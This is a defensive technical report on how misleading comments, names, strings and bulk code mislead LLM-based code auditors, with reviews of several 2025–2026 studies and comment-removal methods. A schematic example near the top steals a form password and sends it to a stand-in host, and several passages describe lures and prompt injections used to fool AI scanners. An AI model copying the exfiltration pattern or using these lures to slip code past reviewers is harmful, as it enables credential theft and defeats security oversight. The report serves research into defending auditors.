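# Protecting language-model code auditors from misleading text: comment removal, truncation, neutral variable names and isolation of custom code

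## What a language-model code auditor reads, and how text in code can mislead it

Source code is the text that programmers write and computers execute. Companies that host, distribute or merge other people's code have good reason to check it first for malware and security flaws. The older method, static analysis, examines code by fixed rules without running it. Many teams now also ask a large language model (LLM), the kind of system behind chatbots such as ChatGPT and Claude, to judge the code. *When AI Agrees Too Much* (Alexopoulos, Alexopoulos and colleagues, 2026) cites a count from late 2025 in which one in seven pull requests (proposed changes to a shared codebase) involved AI review.

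An LLM auditor is a large language model that reads code and gives a security verdict, alone or as part of a pipeline. *The malware that wants your AI scanner to look away* (Cohen, 2026) says that, beyond what fixed rules can do, a model can often understand obfuscated code, which is deliberately hard to read, and explain in plain English what a file is for. The model relies partly on the code's logic and partly on the human language around it. That language is a weakness because whoever wrote the code also wrote it, and can include a lure, which is text meant to push the auditor towards a wrong verdict.

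### A short example

The script below runs on a web page with a login form. It copies the visitor's password and sends it to an address outside the site. The script is schematic, and square brackets stand in for wording and library code.

```
[bundled library, first part: thousands of harmless lines]

// [comment: a claim that this function is safe]
function savePreferences(form) {
  const reviewNote = "[string: a claim that the code passed a review]";
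  const friendlySetting = form.password;
  sendTo("https://outside.example", friendlySetting);
}

[bundled library, second part: thousands more harmless lines]
```

The harm comes from two lines, one that reads the password field and one that sends its contents away. The rest of the script helps hide them. The comment and the string, which no other line uses, are there to mislead the auditor. The variable that holds the password has a harmless-sounding name, and the function's name suggests a routine task. The library does nothing wrong. Web developers routinely pack third-party code into one file with their own, so the library's size is no sign of malice, but it means the auditor has to find a very small amount of harmful code in a large file. The function in the middle is the script's custom logic, the code written for this program rather than copied or bundled library code.

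### One stream of text

A typical scanner gives the model a short instruction to act as a malware analyst and decide whether the following file is dangerous, then pastes in the file. Software splits the instruction and the file into tokens, which are words, fragments of words or symbols, and the model processes them as a single sequence. As Cohen points out, the model cannot reliably detect where the operator's instructions end and the suspect file begins.

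*Prompt injection is not SQL injection (it may be worse)*, a December 2025 post by David C for the United Kingdom's National Cyber Security Centre, explains why this is hard to fix. SQL, the database query language, once had a similar problem, in which text that a visitor typed into a web form could run as a command. Programmers solved it with parameterised queries, which pass the visitor's text to the database separately so that the database can never interpret it as a command. An LLM has no such separation, and only predicts the next token from the text it is given. Developers can mark where the file begins and ends, or train a model to give priority to the operator's instructions. Both can help, but David C regards them as attempts to impose a distinction between instructions and data on a technology that does not make one. He doubts that anyone will ever fully solve the problem.

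The model's context window, the largest amount of text it can take in at once, also limits the length of the stream. If the example script is larger than the window, the pipeline has to truncate it, or leave part of it out. Careless truncation could drop the one function that matters and keep the library.

By contrast, a compiler or a browser's JavaScript engine first parses the file into a syntax tree, in which each piece of the program has a type and a place. In the trees that code-analysis tools build, comments, names and statements are distinct kinds of node. For the example, such a tree would hold a comment node, then a function node containing two declarations and a call. The compiler drops the comment because it does not affect execution. The name `friendlySetting` matters only because it links the two harmful lines, so replacing it with `x` in both places would not change the script's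 behavior. But `password` names a real field of the form, and the script would no longer find that field if the name were changed in the code.

*ALIBI* (Wu and Nita-Rotaru, 2026) describes code as having two channels. The formal channel determines what the program does. The natural-language channel, which the compiler ignores, consists of comments, identifiers (the names that programmers choose for variables, functions, properties and types) and documentation. The string in the example doesn't fit this division neatly. It is a value, so it belongs to the formal channel and a compiler cannot simply discard it, but its contents can be a sentence aimed at the auditor.

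The main reason not to build a model that ignores the natural-language text in code is that the text is useful. Honest developers write down assumptions that a reader could not recover from a single function, such as that every caller has already checked a value. Wu and Nita-Rotaru note that detectors use such context to determine whether an apparent flaw is real, and that verifying every claim would often mean repeating outside analyses, which is impractical. The detector therefore has to give some weight to unverified claims, which lets an attacker mislead it with false ones.

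Identifier names can also mislead a model. *On the Lexical Superstition of Large Language Models for Code Comprehension* (2026) replaced one identifier at a time with a misleading or low-quality name and measured how well models then summarised the code. Changing function names did the most damage, followed by parameters and then local variables, although a function's name appeared on average barely more than once per snippet. *Poisoned Identifiers Survive LLM Deobfuscation* (2026) recounts an earlier experiment by Wang and colleagues in which misleading names hurt analysis more than random strings did. That experiment used older and much smaller models, and summarising code is a different task from judging its safety. Still, the results give some reason to think that a meaningless name is less harmful to an auditor than a false one.

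### Three jobs for an auditor

In malware triage, the auditor judges whether a script or package is malicious. The auditor usually gets the whole file, and if the file is malicious, its author is the opponent and controls every word in it. The example script is a case for malware triage when a stranger uploads it to a hosting platform.

Vulnerability detection is the search for mistakes in code whose developers mostly mean well. Anthropic's coding tool Claude Code, for example, has a command that searches a codebase for problems such as SQL injection, faulty authorisation and insecure data handling. If a careless developer had written the example code so that it sent passwords to an error-logging service, an honest comment saying so would help the auditor. Deleting comments therefore loses more useful information here than in triage, where the developer has a strong reason to lie. Misleading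 text can still appear in this setting. Thornton (2026), in *LLM Code Reviewers Are Harder to Fool Than You Think*, considers malicious insiders and compromised outside libraries, while Wu and Nita-Rotaru consider a coding agent that writes flawed code and comments saying the code is sound.

When reviewing a proposed change, the auditor also reads what the contributor wrote about it, along with the diff, which lists the lines added and removed. In *SEVRA-BENCH* (2026), a test of review agents, the input consists of the state of the repository, the diff, the commit messages (short notes attached to each saved change), and the title, description and inline comments of the pull request. Alexopoulos and colleagues call the diff the substance under review and the rest its presentation. Microsoft (2026) warns that AI workflows embed such user-controlled text directly in the model's prompt. A tool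 that cleans only the source files of a pull request leaves its description unchanged. If the example function arrived in a change described as a way to remember display settings, the auditor would still read that description after every comment in the file had been removed.

Two numbers describe how well the auditor does each job. The detection rate is the share of bad samples that it flags. An auditor that flags 90 of 100 scripts like the example has a detection rate of 90%. The false positive rate is the share of harmless samples that it flags. If it also flags five of 100 similar-looking scripts that really do save display preferences, its false positive rate is 5%.

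A detection rate on its own can be nearly useless, because a model that flags almost every file gives its operator very little information. Alexopoulos and colleagues gave six models 247 vulnerable files and 250 files in which developers had fixed the flaw. Under neutral instructions, Claude Sonnet 4.5 flagged 97.4% of the vulnerable files but cleared only 4.3% of the fixed ones. Some of the flags on fixed files may have pointed to other real defects, so the false positive rate is not necessarily the remaining 95.7%.

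In the same experiment, when the instructions firmly asserted that the files were free of the relevant type of flaw, GPT-4o-mini's detection fell from 97.2% to 3.6%, and the share of fixed files it cleared rose from 3.2% to 98.0%. The model had nearly stopped flagging files, rather than becoming better at telling good code from bad. Claude Opus 4.5's detection fell much less, from 95.7% to 88.8%. For both models, the reassurance was in the operator's prompt, which is more privileged than a comment in the code. *Trusting the Tool* (2026) reports a similar conclusion from Shahriar and colleagues, who added author details, task framings and earlier analysis results to code and found that such cues mainly change how readily a model flags anything.

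### Where the text can sit

Comments are the obvious place for misleading text. Docstrings, the descriptions at the start of a function or module, can also hold it. In Python, they are technically strings that stay attached to the program, so a tool that deletes only what the language defines as a comment will leave them in. Web formats have comments too, which browsers hide from human readers. Microsoft found instructions inside an HTML comment in an issue (a bug report or request on a project's public page). Human readers couldn't see them on the page, but the AI model read them in the raw source.

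Identifiers have little room for an argument, but they can mislead an auditor without one. For example, naming a variable `friendlySetting` removes the clue that the word "password" would have given.

String literals, the pieces of quoted text in a program, remain after comment removal and have already been used in a real attack. Koi Security found a package on npm, the main public registry for JavaScript code, that posed as an extension of a well-known code-checking plugin. It contained a string telling AI scanners to disregard what they knew and assuring them that the code was legitimate. Nothing in the package executed, logged or referred to the string, and Infosecurity Magazine's *Malware Manipulates AI Detection in Latest npm Package Breach* describes it as having no functional role.

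Code that never runs offers more room for misleading text. Sun, Oprea and Wong (2026), in *Syntax- and Compilation-Preserving Evasion of LLM Vulnerability Detectors*, tested four places to put such text without changing a program's behaviour: renamed identifiers, comments, sections that the compiler's settings switch off, and branches whose condition is always false. These branches look like any other code, so an auditor has to work out that the condition can never hold before it can ignore the contents. The branch may also contain its own names and strings.

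An auditor may also read text outside the code. A file's name or folder can suggest that it is a test or a copy of a known library. Documentation can describe a program that behaves differently from the one in the file. Change descriptions can be any length, and in one successful attack by Alexopoulos and colleagues the description included a bogus mathematical proof that the change was secure. An inventory of the text a particular auditor reads should start from the prompt its pipeline assembles, because some pipelines send only the code and others send nearly all of this text.

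### Four effects on the verdict

An attacker can put instructions in the code to try to replace the operator's task with another one, such as reporting that the code has no problems. This is called indirect prompt injection because the attacker leaves the commands in data that the model will later process, rather than sending them to the model directly.

A false claim of safety gives the model apparent evidence that the code is safe, such as a statement that a security team has approved it or that an earlier check makes an attack impossible. The claim is not an instruction, so telling the model to ignore instructions in the file is not enough to protect against it. Studies disagree on how well false claims work. Wu and Nita-Rotaru used comments to get past each of four detectors in more than 90% of cases, while Thornton found only small, statistically non-significant effects across eight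 models. Wu and Nita-Rotaru revised their comments in response to each detector's reasoning, whereas Thornton's comments were fixed, and the two studies tested different detectors.

Dilution is the loss of detection when a few relevant lines sit among much harmless code, even if all of it fits in the context window. It doesn't require text that persuades the model. In the example, the library alone could cause it, even without the comment, the string and the friendly name. Thornton uses "attention dilution" more narrowly, for programs in which long, accurate comments surround the harmless parts and a brief, dismissive one accompanies the flaw. Removing comments would deal with that version but leave the library code in place.

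The fourth effect is that the auditor returns no usable verdict. Cohen examined a sample of the Shai-Hulud worm, which spreads through npm packages. The sample opened with text resembling material that AI safety filters block. In several set-ups the filter cut off the answer, in some cases after the model had begun to describe the malicious code. The verdict is also lost when the pipeline requires a fixed form, such as "malicious" or "benign", and the model returns something it cannot parse. Either failure lets malicious code through if the software counts a missing answer as a pass. Schneier on Security's *Embedding Forbidden Text in Spyware to Discourage AI Analysis* (2026) notes that parsing, string extraction and rule-based detection still work on code that contains such text.

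### The "Notice to AI" scripts

The defences in this report trace back to a script found on Cloudflare's network. Cloudflare's Workers service lets customers run small programs on its servers around the world, and the company uses LLMs to help audit those programs for abuse. In March 2026 its threat-intelligence team, Cloudforce One, was investigating a surge of scripts that turned Workers into VPN and proxy tunnels, many of them built on a protocol called VLESS. One script contained thousands of lines of repetitive comments in several languages, including English, Spanish, Croatian and Estonian, under the heading "Notice to AI".

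Cloudflare (2026) describes the comments as hidden instructions and classifies them as indirect prompt injection, but the portion it published reads more like a false claim of safety. The comments in that portion are addressed to automated reviewers. They describe the file as part of a legitimate private project and list the harmful things that the code supposedly does not do, without any request for a particular verdict.

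The team then ran an experiment, adding lures of this kind to 100 scripts that it already knew to be malicious or abusive and putting them to seven models it does not name, in 18,400 calls. The effect of the lures depended on the model and on the proportion of comments to code, and sheer file size turned out to be the greater obstacle to detection. On 29 April 2026 Cloudflare published the results with five recommendations:

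1. Automated comment removal: delete comments before the analysis.
2. Intentional truncation: with large scripts, give functional code priority over standard text at the top of the file, metadata and the code of software development kits (ready-made libraries from a vendor).
3. Variable anonymisation: replace names that might sway the model with neutral ones such as `variable1`.
4. Specific attack vector prompting: ask whether the script is, say, phishing or a proxy, in place of a general question about abuse.
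5. Semantic intent validation: compare safety claims in the text with what the program does, partly so that legitimate AI applications do not get flagged for overzealous documentation.

Structural isolation uses a program's parsed structure to separate custom logic from library code before the audit. It is not one of the five, but it appears in the report's closing paragraph, with comment removal and variable anonymisation, as part of a general recommendation to reduce noise.

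Cloudflare calls comment removal "trivial but highly effective", but its report does not test that measure or the other four. The experiment varied the number of lures, their language and the size of the file, but did not compare the same scripts before and after a defence. The runs with no added comments come closest, but they show how the models handled the original scripts, not what a removal tool does to a script full of lures. All 100 scripts were bad, so the experiment could not measure a false positive rate for any of the seven models.

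## Measuring how far the auditor is misled before adding a defence

A defence against lures can only recover detections that the auditor misses because of lures. If an auditor misses a malicious script with or without the lure, deleting the lure won't help. The operator therefore first needs to know how many verdicts lures change. To measure this, the operator can give the auditor each sample twice, once in its original form and once with a lure added, while keeping the code that runs, the model, the operator's instructions and the settings the same.

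Each pair has four possible results. If the auditor flags both versions or misses both, the lure did not change the verdict. If it flags the original but misses the version with the lure, it has lost a detection. The reverse is a gained detection. Gains are common, because an auditor may treat lengthy assurances that code is harmless as a sign of malice.

Comparing two different sets of samples is much less reliable than comparing each sample with its own uncommented version. Thornton wrote three elaborate kinds of misleading comment for only the first 30 of 100 vulnerable samples. Detection with these comments seemed 2 to 11 percentage points higher than detection across all 100 samples without comments. But the 30 samples were easier. None was in Java, the language in which the models missed most, and the models found 98.0% of the flaws in them without comments, compared with 90.5% in the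 other 70. When Thornton compared each sample with its own uncommented version, the improvement almost disappeared.

The test should also include harmless code, because some text makes a model more likely to flag any code, vulnerable or not. In *Words Speak Louder Than Code*, Shahriar, Cai and colleagues (2026) gave eight models 435 vulnerable C and C++ functions and a harmless counterpart of each, and varied only the text around the code. Claude Sonnet 4.6 flagged 28.1 percentage points more of the vulnerable functions when told that an automated analysis had marked the code vulnerable than when told it had marked the code safe. It also flagged 32.4 points more of the harmless functions, so a test on vulnerable code alone would have shown a large improvement and missed the rise in false alarms.

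### McNemar's exact test

Some verdicts change for reasons unrelated to the lure. A language model usually picks its words partly at random, so the same prompt can produce "malicious" on one run and "benign" on the next. McNemar's exact test calculates how easily chance could explain a result, using only the pairs in which the verdict changed. If the lure pushed verdicts in neither direction, each changed verdict would be as likely to be a loss as a gain.

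Thornton's result for the model DeepSeek Chat is small enough to work through by hand. Of 100 vulnerable samples, the model flagged 89 without comments and 93 with comments meant to hide the flaw:

| | Flagged with the comments | Missed with the comments |
|---|---|---|
| Flagged without comments | 88 | 1 |
| Missed without comments | 5 | 6 |

Six verdicts changed, with one loss and five gains. If the comments had no effect, each change would be equally likely to be a loss or a gain, giving 2⁶ = 64 equally likely outcomes. One outcome has no losses and six have exactly one, so the chance of at most one loss is 7/64. The chance of at most one gain is the same, so a split at least this uneven would occur 14/64 of the time, or about 22% (p = 0.219). This is above the conventional significance threshold of 0.05, so the result gives no good reason to think that the comments helped or harmed detection.

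If n verdicts changed and the smaller of the two groups has k members, then p = 2 × [C(n,0) + C(n,1) + … + C(n,k)] / 2ⁿ, where C(n,i) is the number of ways to choose i items from n. If the groups are the same size, p is 1.

A small test of how far an auditor is misled can easily miss a large effect. In *Trusting the Tool*, deepseek-chat judged 83 vulnerable functions alongside notes from a static analysis tool. Given false notes that a missing safety check was present, the model lost ten detections and gained one compared with true notes about the same operations, a significant result (p = 0.012). A larger DeepSeek model lost four detections and gained none, a fall of 14 percentage points, but it judged only 29 functions and the result was not significant (p = 0.125).

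McNemar's test also detects only a net shift. Shahriar and colleagues attributed the same code to either a principal security engineer or a newly hired junior developer. Claude Sonnet 4.6 found 12 flaws only when the code was attributed to the junior developer and 15 only when it was attributed to the engineer, so 27 verdicts changed but its average hardly moved. They interpret this as two opposing effects that cancel out, but some of the changes could be random.

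Two controls help to show whether the misleading text itself changed the verdicts. The operator can run the unmodified samples twice and count the verdicts that change. Because almost any edit to a prompt flips some verdicts, the operator can also replace the misleading text with neutral text of similar length. *Trusting the Tool* dropped one explanation of its results after content-neutral changes to the prompt flipped a similar number of verdicts.

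### Malicious scripts with added lures

Cloudflare ran the larger of the two security experiments, using 100 real abusive scripts that its production blocking rules had already caught. Of these, 52 were for phishing, 35 for proxies and tunnels, seven for file hosting and six for streaming abuse. The team tested 23 variants of each script, with up to 1,000 added comments in English, Estonian, Arabic, Mandarin Chinese or Russian. A program inserted the comments at random points between statements, and each model received as much of the script as its context window allowed. In an earlier round of 2,700 calls, the team had put the misleading comments in one block at the top of snippets of about 1,500 words. Those comments mostly backfired, raising detection for most of the cheaper models.

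The company divides its seven models into three flagship "frontier" models and four faster, cheaper ones. Their detection rates were:

| Model | No added comments | 20 comments | 1,000 comments |
|---|---|---|---|
| Frontier 1 | 67% | 67% | 76% |
| Frontier 2 | 61% | 64% | 68% |
| Frontier 3 | 62% | 67% | 75% |
| Non-frontier 1 | 90% | 67% | 72% |
| Non-frontier 2 | 65% | 75% | 91% |
| Non-frontier 3 | 72% | 67% | 68% |
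| Non-frontier 4 | 59% | 65% | 72% |

The columns average 68.0%, 67.4% and 74.6%. Twenty comments barely changed the average, but only because a 23-point fall by non-frontier model 1, the best of the seven on the original scripts, offset several smaller rises.

Cloudflare doesn't publish the numbers of lost and gained detections, so readers can't run McNemar's test on the exact figures, but the totals limit the possible results. If non-frontier model 1 gave a usable verdict on all 100 scripts, it missed ten of the originals, so it can have gained at most ten detections. If it gained all ten, it lost 33. Even that split gives p ≈ 0.0006, so chance is a poor explanation, even though this was the worst affected of seven models. Non-frontier model 3 fell by five points, and the most lopsided split that fits its totals, five losses and no gains, gives only p = 0.063. An operator using model 1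 would therefore have a serious problem with lures, but the totals aren't enough to tell whether the same is true of model 3.

With 1,000 comments, five of the seven models flagged more scripts than they had originally. The language of the comments also mattered at that volume. Non-frontier model 3 flagged 68% of the scripts with English comments and 82% with Russian ones, while non-frontier model 2 flagged 91% with English comments and 84% with Arabic ones. A test with comments in one language may therefore misjudge the risk from comments in another.

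Frontier models 1 and 3 sometimes returned garbled text or a refusal when given the largest numbers of comments. How a test counts such answers can change its result. Cloudflare excluded malformed answers from its table of detection by comment ratio, whereas *Trusting the Tool* counts an answer without a verdict as wrong. If the operator's software treats a missing verdict as a pass, the test should count it as a missed detection.

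The published totals have an unexplained discrepancy. Seven models, 23 variants and 100 scripts would give 16,100 calls, but Cloudflare reports 18,400. It also reports 789 valid verdicts on the original scripts, but seven models could give at most 700. Both numbers would fit eight sets of calls, perhaps from an eighth model or a repeated run.

### The claimed "bypass zone"

Cloudflare argues that the number of comments matters less than their share of the file. It grouped the verdicts on the English variants by that share:

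| Comments as a share of the file | Valid verdicts | Detection rate |
|---|---|---|
| 0% (original) | 789 | 67.3% |
| Under 1% | 2,528 | 53.3% |
| 1–10% | 822 | 77.0% |
| 25–50% | 283 | 97.9% |
| Over 50% | 439 | 98.9% |

The table has no row for 10–25%. Based on the second row, the company describes a "bypass zone" below 1%, where lures slightly shift the model's reasoning without raising suspicion.

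The rows can't be compared directly because they contain different mixes of scripts. If the same 20 comments totalled 2,000 characters, they would make up about 4% of a 50-kilobyte script but less than 0.1% of a three-megabyte one. The under-1% row must therefore lean towards large files, and the models did badly on those even without lures, flagging only 17.6% of files over three megabytes. Comparing the rows repeats the mistake of comparing Thornton's 30 easy samples with the full set of 100, but with the error in the other direction.

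Cloudflare's figures by file size allow a rough check. Without lures, the 64 scripts over 100 kilobytes had an average detection rate of about 51.5%, close to the 53.3% in the supposed bypass zone. Comparing scripts within the same size group is more informative. Adding one or 20 comments changed a group's detection rate by at most 7.2 points, and that largest change was in a group of only three scripts. No group showed the 14-point fall seen between the first two rows of the table. Lures may do some harm in large files, but file size could account for most of the apparent bypass zone.

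File size also distorts the other end of the table. Lures can make up a quarter or more of a file only if the file is fairly small, and the models flagged at least 94% of scripts under 500 kilobytes before anyone added a comment. The near-perfect detection above 25% is therefore weak evidence that adding many lures makes an attack easier to detect. To test either claim properly, the company would need to compare each altered script with its own original.

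### Short samples with known flaws

In a single-author preprint published in February 2026, Thornton, a security professional, tested vulnerability detection in much shorter code. Thornton wrote 100 samples (50 in Python, 30 in JavaScript and 20 in Java), each with one known flaw and most 15 to 60 lines long. Five commercial and three open-source models reviewed the samples without comments and then with comments meant to hide the flaw, for example by claiming that someone had already reviewed the code.

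| Model | Samples | Without comments | With misleading comments | Lost | Gained | p |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| Claude Opus 4.6 | 100 | 95.0% | 94.0% | 1 | 0 | 1.000 |
| GPT-5.2 | 99 | 93.0% | 91.9% | 3 | 2 | 1.000 |
| Gemini 2.5 Pro | 99 | 91.9% | 91.9% | 4 | 4 | 1.000 |
| DeepSeek Chat | 100 | 89.0% | 93.0% | 1 | 5 | 0.219 |
| Perplexity Sonar Pro | 75 | 96.1% | 92.0% | 5 | 2 | 0.453 |
| Llama 3.3 70B | 100 | 72.0% | 71.0% | 12 | 11 | 1.000 |
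| Qwen 2.5 72B | 100 | 70.0% | 72.0% | 10 | 12 | 0.832 |
| DeepSeek-Coder-V2 16B | 100 | 53.0% | 58.0% | 12 | 17 | 0.458 |

None of the eight results is close to significant. The commercial models also reviewed a version with neutral comments, and their detection rates were within about three points of their rates with misleading comments. The differences between models were far larger than any effect of the comments.

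Thornton counts 14 "induced misses" among the commercial models, meaning flaws that a model found in the bare code but missed when misleading comments were added. But the same models also gained 13 detections with the comments, so many of the 14 may be ordinary variation between runs. Thornton could not check this because each combination was run only once. One case is harder to attribute to chance, because three models missed the same flaw, in a multi-step authorisation routine in Java, after the comments were added. An attacker with a single flaw to hide needs only one such case, even if the comments have no effect on average.

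The experiment was also too small to rule out a modest effect. Thornton regards five extra misses per 100 flaws as the smallest change that matters in practice. If the comments caused a model to miss an extra 5% of the flaws and never helped it find one, a test with 100 samples would give a significant result only about 38% of the time, because significance requires at least six lost detections. Thornton argues that the design was sensitive enough to find an effect of this size, but uses a looser threshold of p < 0.10.

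The scoring could also have hidden some losses, because a program counted a flaw as found if the model's answer contained a keyword for that type of flaw. A comment that names a flaw to deny it gives the model a keyword to repeat. Thornton reasons that any bias cancels out because the same keywords applied to both versions, but the bare code has no comment to repeat. Thornton checked 14 answers to the more elaborate comments and found one that repeated a keyword this way, but that sample is too small to establish how often it happened.

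Every sample was vulnerable, so this experiment, like Cloudflare's, could not measure a false positive rate. A model that flagged every sample as vulnerable would have looked perfectly resistant to lures.

### A larger effect in a different task

*CodeCrash* (Lam, Wang and colleagues, 2025) found that models were much easier to mislead when they had to work out what code does. The main task was to predict the output of a short Python function for a given input. Altering the code reduced performance across 17 models by 23.2% on average, and by 13.8% when the models reasoned step by step before answering.

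These are relative falls, and changes to the code itself, such as meaningless names, convoluted conditions and code that never runs, make up half the weight in the average. But misleading text alone had a similar effect. When the models answered directly, Lam and colleagues measured average falls of 24.1% for false descriptive comments, 23.6% for false messages in print statements and 19.7% for comments hinting at a wrong answer. The absolute fall for descriptive comments was about 13 percentage points. With step-by-step reasoning, the three relative falls shrank to 14.9%, 19.6% and 6.2%.

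Code length can't explain why Thornton found a much smaller effect, because both experiments used short code. The age of the models can't fully explain it either, because Llama 3.3 70B and Qwen 2.5 72B were tested in both. In the other experiment, false descriptive comments lowered each model's success at predicting outputs by about 15%, but on Thornton's samples their detection rates changed by only one or two points.

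The task is a better explanation, because a model predicting an output has to get every step right, and one false belief about a loop or condition can make the answer wrong. A reviewer can often recognise a flaw by its form, such as a database query that includes unchecked user input, and Thornton suggests that this makes vulnerability detection harder to disrupt. Lam and colleagues have some evidence that the task matters even when the code and the type of comment stay the same. When models had to find an input that would produce a given output, average performance rose by 4.2% with false descriptive comments. Several inputs could be correct, and the comments happened to encourage shortcuts that led to valid answers.

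The task may also explain why large numbers of comments had different effects. Lam and colleagues found that performance fell further as they added more false comments, whereas most of Cloudflare's models were more likely to treat code as suspicious when it had 1,000 comments. In malware triage, a thousand comments insisting that code is harmless are themselves evidence of malicious intent, but the programmer's intent has little bearing on predicting a program's output.

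The studies also disagree less than they first appear to. When the models reasoned step by step, false descriptive comments lowered output prediction accuracy by about 8% for Llama 3.3 70B and 7% for Qwen 2.5 72B. A similar relative drop on Thornton's samples would have been about five percentage points, which a test with 100 samples could easily miss.

How far the auditor is misled also depends on the attacker. Thornton's results with fixed comments are weak evidence about an attacker who keeps revising a comment in response to the detector. Wu and Nita-Rotaru found that such revision made their attacks more successful. They also tested vulnerability detection, so working on that task does not by itself protect an auditor.

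Code length is more useful for comparing Thornton with Cloudflare. In Cloudflare's scripts under 100 kilobytes, 20 comments raised average detection from 94.1% to 99.0%, so fixed lures generally failed in short code in both experiments. In the largest scripts, the models detected so little without lures that adding them could not lower detection much.

### Newer models

Newer models have replaced those that Thornton named. Cloudflare did not name its models, so nobody outside the company can repeat its tests on them or their successors. The closest evidence on models from summer 2026 is in *Trusting the Tool*, which tests kimi-k3, qwen3.7-flash and deepseek-v4.1-flash. The false claims in its tests were in notes from a static analysis tool, which the models had more reason to trust than comments.

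The researchers added seven models to confirm their first results. In four of them, false assurances lowered detection by 13 to 19 points compared with true notes about the same operations. False alarms, which claimed that a fixed function still lacked a check, never significantly lowered accuracy. In some models they raised it, apparently because the model looked for the check and found it. Across the seven models, false assurances moved verdicts towards their claim by an average of 16 points more than false alarms did.

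All seven models ran with their built-in reasoning switched off, although the prompt asked them to work step by step. It is unclear how much built-in reasoning would change the results. Two earlier configurations in *Trusting the Tool* used it. False assurances did not lower detection in one, but the other, the larger DeepSeek model, lost four detections out of 29. An operator who switches to a new model or changes its reasoning setting therefore has to measure the effect of lures again.

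## Removing comments

If an operator finds that lures change verdicts, the most direct response is to delete comments before the model reads the code. This also removes honest developers' comments, and it leaves lures in strings, names and other text. Cloudflare recommends the step but didn't test it, so evidence on its benefits and drawbacks must come mostly from other experiments.

### The procedure

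The pipeline makes a copy without comments for the model and keeps the original. Nobody runs the copy, but its code has to mean the same as the original's, or the model will audit a different program.

1. Parse the file with a parser for its language. Tree-sitter, a widely used parsing library, keeps comments in its syntax trees and records where each one starts and ends.
2. Mark the comment nodes for deletion, except the few that other tools need.
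3. Decide whether to mark docstrings as well.
4. Cut out the marked text, working from the end of the file to the start so that the recorded positions stay correct. Put a space in place of each comment, or a line break if the comment ran over several lines. Then delete any line that held only a comment and is now empty.
5. Parse the copy and check that its tree matches the original's, apart from the deleted nodes.
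6. Save a line map, which links each line of the copy to its line in the original, so that the auditor's report can point to the right place.

In JavaScript, a line break directly after `return` ends the statement, even if the break is inside a comment. A function with a multi-line comment between `return` and a value therefore returns nothing. If the tool deletes the comment and joins the two parts, the function shown to the model returns the value.

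Some comments affect how other tools build or check a program. In Go, a build tag (a comment starting with `//go:build`) specifies which systems a file is for. In older Python code, type comments give the types of variables for a type checker. Both help the model understand the code, so the pipeline can keep them if they match the tool's exact syntax. Without that condition, an attacker could prevent a lure from being removed by starting it with the same few characters.

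Suppression comments need different treatment from other comments because they also affect scanners. For example, `# nosec` tells Bandit, a security scanner for Python, to skip a line. This amounts to a claim that the line is safe, so the pipeline should delete the comment from the model's copy of the code and also have Bandit ignore the comment.

In malware triage, docstrings deserve the same suspicion as comments. But a Python program can read its own docstrings, and some command-line tools print them as help text, so the pipeline should check whether the code uses them before deleting them. If a docstring is a function's entire body, the pipeline must replace it with `pass`, Python's instruction to do nothing. JavaScript code can retrieve a function's source text, including its comments, which lets malware store data in the comments. A script that retrieves source text this way needs closer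 analysis with its comments intact.

For a proposed change, the pipeline should remove comments from the complete old and new files and then compute the diff. A diff shows only fragments, and a fragment may begin inside a comment or string, which a parser cannot recognize without the preceding text.

### Comment markers inside strings

A search pattern that deletes everything from `//` to the end of the line may look like an easier method. In the example script, it would also match the `//` in the web address, and reduce the line that sends the password away to this:

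```
  sendTo("https:
```

The tool has deleted the destination and the variable that holds the password, which are some of the best evidence of theft. A parser avoids this mistake because it treats the whole address as a string. An attacker could also exploit a pattern that doesn't recognize strings by putting an opening comment marker in one string and a closing marker in a later one, so that the tool deletes the working code between them.

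Bidirectional controls are invisible Unicode characters that let writers mix languages such as Arabic and English by changing the order in which a screen displays text. In source code, they can make a working statement look like part of a comment, or the reverse. The parser reads the characters in their stored order and still finds the real comments, but the display may mislead a person comparing the comment-free copy with the original. Zero-width characters take up no space on the screen and can split a word such as "password" so that a search for it fails.

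*enclawed* (2026), which describes a security framework for AI assistants, lists the characters that its tool strips from untrusted text, including nine bidirectional controls (U+202A to U+202E and U+2066 to U+2069) and five zero-width characters (U+200B to U+200D, U+2060 and U+FEFF). For code, replacing each one with a visible escape sequence such as `\u202E` and recording its position is safer than deleting it. Deleting a character from a string would change the string's value, and some of these characters have legitimate uses, for example in Persian text and in emoji. The tool also replaces every ASCII control character except the tab. Taken literally, that would include the line feed, which a code auditor has to keep.

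### The example script after removal

The model would receive this copy of the example script:

```
[bundled library, first part, without its comments]

function savePreferences(form) {
  const reviewNote = "[string: a claim that the code passed a review]";
  const friendlySetting = form.password;
  sendTo("https://outside.example", friendlySetting);
}

[bundled library, second part, without its comments]
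```

Removing the comment deletes the claim that the function is safe and leaves both harmful lines intact. It doesn't change the string containing the claim that the code passed a review, the two friendly names or the library around the function. Suppose the comment was on line 4,001 of the original and no comments came before it. The tool deletes that whole line, so the line that reads the password moves from 4,004 to 4,003. The line map makes it possible to report the original number.

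### Which comments to remove

Removing every comment is the simplest policy. The tool doesn't have to judge what a comment means, so an attacker cannot get a misleading comment past it through clever wording. The policy also removes comments that stop the auditor from answering at all. *A JavaScript Comment That Made AI Security Scanners Give Up on Analysis* (2026) describes a June 2026 case in which attackers added 99 lines of comments to a credential-stealing script and hid the script in Python packages.

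A narrower policy is to remove only claims that the auditor cannot check against the code it can see, such as a statement that a function in another file has already validated the input. Wu and Nita-Rotaru tested such a filter on misleading comments that they had tailored to four vulnerability detectors. The filter reduced evasion rates to between 0.4% and 2.8%. Without a defence, the comments had caused each detector to miss more than 90% of the flaws it could otherwise find.

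The improvement is probably smaller than it looks from those figures. Without a defence, the attack counted as successful on a flaw if any of ten styles of comment worked, but the rates for the filter appear to count each comment separately. If 2.5% of comments got through and the ten styles succeeded independently, the chance of at least one success would be 1 − 0.975¹⁰, or about 22%. The styles probably succeed on many of the same flaws, so the real figure would be lower, but it could still be well above 2.5%.

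Wu and Nita-Rotaru also didn't let the attacker revise its comments in response to the filter, though they did for their other defences. One of those defences let through attacks on 18.3% of the flaws that one detector could find, and on 49.6% after five rounds of revision.

The filter would probably remove many honest comments too, because a statement that every caller has checked a value cannot be verified from a single file, even when it is true. The published rates cover only attacks, so they do not measure how much useful information the filter deletes.

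A tool can also look for suspicious text of any kind. *CodeSentinel* (Cheng, Yu and colleagues, 2026) describes one for coding models that retrieve outside code. It uses Tree-sitter to find comments, strings, identifiers and decoy code that may contain hidden instructions, then removes or neutralises them. Its average F1 score across six families of attack was 0.80. F1 combines the share of planted items found with the share of flagged items that really were planted. If both shares were 80%, the tool would miss one planted item in five, and one in five of its deletions would be a mistake. The score measures how well the tool finds planted text, not how it affects a security auditor's verdicts.

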